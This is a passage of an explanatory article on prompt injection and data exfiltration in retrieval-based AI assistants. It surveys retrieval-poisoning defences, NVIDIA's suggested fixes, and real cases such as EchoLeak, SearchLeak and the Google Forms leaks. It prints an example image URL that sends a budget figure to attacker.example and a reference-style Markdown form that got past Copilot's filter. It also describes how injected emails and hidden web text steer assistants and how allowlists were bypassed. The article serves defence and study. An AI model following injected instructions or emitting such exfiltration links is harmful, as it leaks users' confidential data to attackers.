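Other defences inspect passages after the search. Dahal and Xiong (2026), in *Prevented is Not Protected*, retested several of them using *PoisonedRAG*'s texts and a small Llama model. On 100 questions with one poisoned passage each, the undefended model endorsed the attacker's answer 35 times. TrustRAG, which filters passages and resolves conflicts between them, cut this to 11. Telling the model to be cautious about unreliable evidence raised the count to 61.

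Dahal and Xiong also tested a detector that looks for unusual search scores. It caught 59 of 60 bad answers when one retrieved passage was poisoned, but none when all five were. Such a detector can't work if the attacker wrote every retrieved passage, because none of them stands out. *GuardRAG* (2026), a defence that examines the retrieved passages as a group, may have the same problem. But some attacks, such as *ToxicRAG* (2026), now use only one document per question, and these defences are more likely to work against one document than against five.

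Published success rates for defences deserve some scepticism. Liu and colleagues reviewed 118 papers, of which 108 reported an improvement. They had concerns about the independence of the testing in 109, because researchers almost always test their own defences. Only 11 papers let the attacker query the system repeatedly and adapt to the responses.

### Testing the recommended fixes

NVIDIA's 2025 post recommends four fixes aimed at the documents themselves. The table applies them to three attackers: a stranger who sends an email, a stranger who shares a file, and a dishonest colleague who adds a page to the company's shared documents.

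| Fix | Malicious email | Shared file | Dishonest colleague |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exclude external email or search it separately | Works unless the user asks about that email | No effect | No effect |
| Let users limit the search to their own or the company's documents | No effect unless the limit covers email | Works | Works only for "my documents" |
| Check that passages are on topic | Catches unrelated instructions | Catches unrelated instructions | Misses a false claim about the topic |
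| Answer from a tightly controlled collection | Works for subjects the collection covers | Works for subjects the collection covers | Works unless the colleague can edit it |

Separating external email stops a stranger's message from affecting an answer about parental leave, but it can't protect a summary of the inbox, which has to include the message.

Search limits work only if users choose them well. The "my documents" setting is the only one that excludes a dishonest colleague's files, but it also excludes the parental leave policy, because the human resources department owns it. Most people will probably choose "all documents" and keep that setting, so the company's documents would be a better default.

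The topic check is the weakest of the four because a poisoned passage must resemble the question to be retrieved, and that resemblance also helps it pass the check. The check could still catch an email that opens with words about travel expenses and then asks for server keys, but it would miss a page that gives the wrong deadline for claiming those expenses.

Controlled collections offer the best protection. If the assistant answers questions about leave only from documents that human resources maintains, neither stranger can affect those answers, and a dishonest colleague would need editing rights. Harang recommended building specialised bots around such collections, and said the key lesson of the case was to limit RAG to vetted, authoritative sources. He also wanted answers to link to their sources, so that a user can see when a claim about company policy came from a stranger's file. However,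 some material, such as customers' latest messages, has no authoritative collection.

NVIDIA concedes that restricting write access "can be quite difficult" because assistants often need text that other people wrote. An assistant asked to summarise the day's email, for example, would have little to summarise if it ignored messages from others. Chaudhari and colleagues reached a similar conclusion about accepting only documents from verified sources, which would require someone to run the verification and would leave the assistant with less information.

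NVIDIA says other parts of the design have to protect applications like these. An assistant that only writes summaries might give its user a false one, but it can't send the user's files to the attacker without a tool or link that reaches the outside world.

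## Links and images that carry data to an attacker

An assistant with no tools can still send data out if its chat window turns the model's text into working links and images. This is the third weakness on NVIDIA's list. It usually involves Markdown, a simple way of formatting plain text, in which a link and an image look like this:

```markdown
[Leave policy](https://intranet.example/leave)
![Team photo](https://intranet.example/team.png)
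```

In Markdown, an image is written the same way as a link, except that it starts with an exclamation mark. Many chat applications convert the model's Markdown into HTML, the language of web pages, and the browser shows a clickable link or a picture.

### How an image leaks data

Suppose a finance manager asks the example assistant about next year's budget, and the search retrieves the budget along with an outsider's email that contains an indirect prompt injection.

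1. The model follows the injected instructions and ends its answer with an image from the attacker's site. It puts the budget figure in the image's address, as in `https://attacker.example/pixel.png?d=4200000`.
2. The chat window converts the answer to HTML.
3. The browser requests the image immediately, as it does for any image on a page.
4. The attacker's server records the requested address in its log, including the 4200000, and sends back a transparent image one pixel wide.

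The manager sees an ordinary answer and doesn't have to click anything. A link can carry the same data, but the browser sends it only if the user clicks, so the attacker needs a tempting label, such as NVIDIA's example, "click here to learn more!"

The address behind that label ends in `Tm93IHlvdSdyZSBqdXN0IHNob3dpbmcgb2ZmIDsp`. This is Base64, a standard way of writing any data with letters, digits and a few symbols. It uses no key, so anyone can decode it with a free tool. The string decodes to "Now you're just showing off ;)". Base64 hides the data from a user who glances at the link and from a filter that searches for words like "password", but not from the person reading the server log.

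### Who found it

NVIDIA writes that the problem has been known since Johann Rehberger published about it in mid-2023, but Roman Samoilenko had published it earlier. His *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* described stealing chat data with a one-pixel Markdown image, and Willison (2023) linked to it on 14 April in a blog post of the same title. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, Rehberger credits Samoilenko with finding the flaw at the end of March and says that he himself came across it independently a few days later.

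Samoilenko's attack used a website that secretly added instructions to any text a visitor copied from it. If the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, the model could add the invisible image to every later answer and send out each new question. The attack didn't always work, and Samoilenko found passwords much harder to extract than prompts or code.

In a demonstration against Microsoft's Bing Chat, Rehberger showed that a comment or advertisement on a web page was enough to steal other data from the same page, without the victim pasting anything. According to his blog post, Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, he reported this to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and learned on 15 June that a fix was in place. The fix included a rule that let the page load images from only four Bing addresses.

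OpenAI didn't introduce its first mitigation until December 2023, when ChatGPT's web page began checking with an OpenAI server that each image address was safe before displaying the image. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes gaps in this check, including that the iPhone app didn't have it. Rehberger also set up one image address for each of the 36 letters and digits, and nine of them passed the check, which was enough to spell out "hi" in two requests.

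### Limiting where images can come from

NVIDIA's first fix is the kind of rule Microsoft gave Bing Chat, a content security policy (CSP) that lists the sites a page may load images from. The server sends the rule along with the page:

```http
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://images.example.com
```

Here `'self'` means the application's own site, so the browser doesn't request images in the model's answer from anywhere else, however the attacker wrote the Markdown. HuggingChat, Hugging Face's chat application, needed a rule like this. In PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*, a user uploads confidential quarterly figures and adds a web page of customer reviews to the chat. Hidden text on the page makes the model put the figures into an image address on the attacker's domain, and the browser sends them there when it loads the image.

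W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the web standard, says CSP is "not intended as a first line of defense" against injected content. `img-src` covers only images, so a developer should also set `default-src`, which covers most other things a page can load. Neither stops a user from clicking a link to another site. Only the browser enforces CSP, so it has no effect on requests from a server or an agent's tools.

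Attackers have used that last gap to get past long allowlists. EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) was an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches a company's email, files and chats. The attacker only had to send an email written to match many likely questions and wait for the user to ask Copilot one of them. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) explains how the security company Aim Security built it. The researchers got an image into Copilot's answer, but Microsoft's CSP stopped the browser from loading it from their server. However, one of the 29 different entries on the policy's list covered Microsoft Teams, and a Teams service would fetch any web address it was given. The browser contacted Teams, and Teams contacted the researchers' server with the stolen data in the address.

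The same list contained `*.bing.com`. A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described an attack on Copilot's enterprise search (CVE-2026-42824) that went through Bing. Bing's search-by-image feature fetches a picture from whatever address it receives, so it could pass data to an attacker just as Teams had. Microsoft (2025) had listed "deterministic blocking of known data exfiltration methods" among its defences in the month after EchoLeak became public, but the Bing route presumably wasn't known then.

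Varonis advises companies to look for allowed sites that fetch addresses supplied by users. That's good advice, but it would have missed the flaw in the email application Superhuman, whose policy allowed `docs.google.com`. That site also hosts Google Forms, and a form's owner can create a link that submits an answer as soon as a browser requests it. In PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, an injected email made the assistant use such a link as an image address, with other emails as the answer. Google stored the emails in the form, where the attacker could read them, and didn't forward anything. One response leaked parts of more than 40 emails.

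An allowed site is therefore safe only if an attacker can't make it forward a request and can't read what it stores. Large sites with many services rarely meet that standard, but a server the company controls that only serves fixed image files usually does. Companies that load outside images through their own server also need to make sure it doesn't become a way around the policy, as PromptArmor warned the note-taking company Notion.

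### Checking the whole address

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) argues that lists of trusted sites are not enough, partly because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere. ChatGPT instead loads an address automatically only if OpenAI's web crawler has already seen that exact address on the public web. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, so an address it has seen is unlikely to contain their private data. For any other address, ChatGPT either tries a different site or shows the user a warning.

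This rule would stop the Google Forms attack, because a form link containing somebody's emails wouldn't be on the public web. An attacker can still send information by choosing which existing pages ChatGPT loads. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* points out that an attacker could use a blog with 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit, or even thousands of pages. With 2,000 pages, an attacker could assign 1,000 to the first three digits of a six-digit login code and 1,000 to the last three, and learn the code from two requests. Rehberger suggests stopping the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, which would make it harder to spell out a long message but wouldn't protect the login code.

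Rehberger also warned that some of OpenAI's developers might not know about the check or use it. Less than three months after OpenAI described the check, PromptArmor reported that the Google Forms attack worked on Codex, OpenAI's agent for coding and office work. In PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*, a user asks Codex to sort their email, and an injected message makes Codex send the other emails to the attacker's form. Either Codex didn't have the check or the check failed.

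### Links that need a click

NVIDIA recommends showing a link's full address before the browser connects, or making links inactive so that the user has to copy and paste them. Both measures give a careful user a chance to notice an unfamiliar site. But a long address full of Base64 looks much like the tracking links in ordinary newsletters, and a user who pastes it into a browser still sends the data.

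People learn to ignore frequent warnings, just as they do an agent's approval requests, so OpenAI warns users only about addresses that the crawler hasn't seen. It warns them that the link may contain information from the conversation. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes showing the user the information that would be sent. This is more useful than showing the raw address, because most people can't read Base64 but can judge whether they want to send a budget to a stranger.

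A link can leak data before anyone clicks it if a company's assistant replies through a chat application such as Slack or Telegram. These applications fetch the linked page as soon as the reply arrives to show a preview, and PromptArmor notes that this makes the same kind of request as a click. NVIDIA's post doesn't mention previews, so a developer who followed its advice on links could easily miss this risk.

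Links can also harm users without leaking data. In *ChatGPhish*, the security company Permiso describes adding instructions to a web page and asking ChatGPT to summarise it. ChatGPT wrote a normal summary followed by a fake security alert with a link to the attacker's site. In other tests, the alert contained an image, which gave the attacker the user's internet address, browser type and the time of the request. This leak is much smaller than the others because it included nothing from the conversation.

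OpenAI's check is meant to keep private data out of addresses, and these image addresses contained no private data. Rehberger believes ChatGPT also trusts any address in the user's own message. Permiso used a Firefox feature that passes the page's text to ChatGPT, which may be why the images loaded.

Showing the full link would have helped against the fake alert, because the domain had nothing to do with OpenAI. It wouldn't have helped against Permiso's other version, in which the image was a QR code, because the user scans the code with a phone and the address never appears on the computer. An image allowlist is the better defence against the QR code, provided the attacker can't host pictures on an allowed site.

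### Removing links and images from the output

NVIDIA's third fix is to sanitize the model's output, which means removing Markdown, HTML and web addresses before displaying it. Microsoft 365 Copilot already did some of this when Aim Security attacked it. Copilot removed outside links and images written in the usual way, but Markdown also lets a writer put the address on a separate line:

```markdown
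![Team photo][1]

[1]: https://intranet.example/team.png
```

Copilot's filter didn't recognise this form. A developer can avoid the problem by converting the answer to HTML and filtering it before the browser receives it. Every image is then the same HTML element, however the model wrote it, so the filter can delete all images except those from approved addresses without handling every Markdown variation.

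The filter also has to run before the browser requests any images. In SearchLeak, the user clicked a genuine microsoft.com link that contained the attacker's instructions, and Copilot searched the user's mailbox. Microsoft's filter turned any HTML in the answer into harmless text, but only once the answer was complete. Copilot displays answers as the model writes them, so the browser had already requested the image. The demonstration stole only the subject line of an email, but subject lines sometimes contain login codes. Varonis recommends sanitizing each piece of the answer as the browser displays it.

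Google is stricter about images. The security company Checkmarx quotes Google as saying that Gemini's sanitizer identifies external image URLs and doesn't render them, and that the image leak in EchoLeak therefore doesn't apply to Gemini.

### How vendors responded

| Case | What the vendor did |
|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Microsoft received the report in January 2025 and fixed the flaw on its own servers in May |
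| HuggingChat | Hugging Face received the report on 1 December 2025 and hadn't replied when PromptArmor published |
| Superhuman AI | Superhuman received the report on Friday 5 December 2025, switched off the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday |
| Codex | OpenAI received the report on 21 April 2026 and had fixed the flaw by 21 May |
| ChatGPhish | OpenAI received the report on 29 April 2026, said it couldn't reproduce the problem, and later marked a revised report as a duplicate |
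| SearchLeak | Microsoft assigned a CVE on 4 June 2026 and had patched the flaw by 15 June |

Reddy and Gujral's *EchoLeak* (2025) gives the EchoLeak dates and reports that Microsoft began removing the separate-line links and embedded images from incoming outside content. The patches also reportedly included options to stop Copilot from using outside messages in some situations. Microsoft found no sign that anyone had used the attack against customers. The Next Web gives the date of the SearchLeak CVE. Microsoft rated that flaw critical, but The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reports more moderate severity scores of 6.5 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database.

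Vendors don't always agree that these leaks are flaws. Checkmarx reports that Microsoft didn't consider a no-click leak in Copilot Chat a vulnerability, so it did not commit to fixing it.

### Turning active content off

NVIDIA's fourth fix, offered "as a last resort", is to disable active content in the user interface, so that the chat window shows the model's answer as plain text. This is the most complete of the four fixes, because nobody has to decide which sites are trustworthy or recognise every way of writing a link. Even if the model writes an image in an unusual form, the user sees only the markup, and the browser doesn't request the image.

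NVIDIA doesn't explain why it lists such a strong fix last, but the reason is probably the inconvenience to users. Plain text makes it tedious to follow the source links that Harang recommended, and it removes the charts and pictures that some applications exist to show. NVIDIA's order makes sense if it ranks the fixes from least to most disruptive for users, but not if it ranks them by strength.

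Some companies have accepted at least part of that drawback. Samoilenko argued in 2023 that ChatGPT shouldn't display Markdown images at all. Willison noted in January 2024 that Amazon had fixed a leak in its business assistant, Q, by preventing it from outputting links, and that Microsoft 365's chat apparently did the same. EchoLeak later got links past Microsoft's filter. This is a good reason to switch off active content in the interface, as NVIDIA advises, instead of trying to delete every link from the text.

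A developer can keep source links without letting the model write any addresses. The model cites the second retrieved document as "2", and the application turns that number into a link using the address in its own index. A hijacked model could cite the wrong document, but it couldn't add the budget to the link. Charts can work the same way if the developer's own code draws them. This approach applies NVIDIA's advice about generated code to links. It would suit the example assistant well, since nearly everything it needs to link to is already in the index, but would be less suitable for a web search assistant, which users expect to link to pages across the internet.

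Showing an agent's output as plain text doesn't stop the agent from leaking data through its tools. Superhuman's assistant could open web pages to answer questions, and PromptArmor made it open an address on the attacker's site with the contents of the user's inbox added to the address. The leak didn't require an image to appear or anyone to click a link, so none of the four display fixes would have helped. The assistant needed egress control, or a check like OpenAI's on every address it opened.
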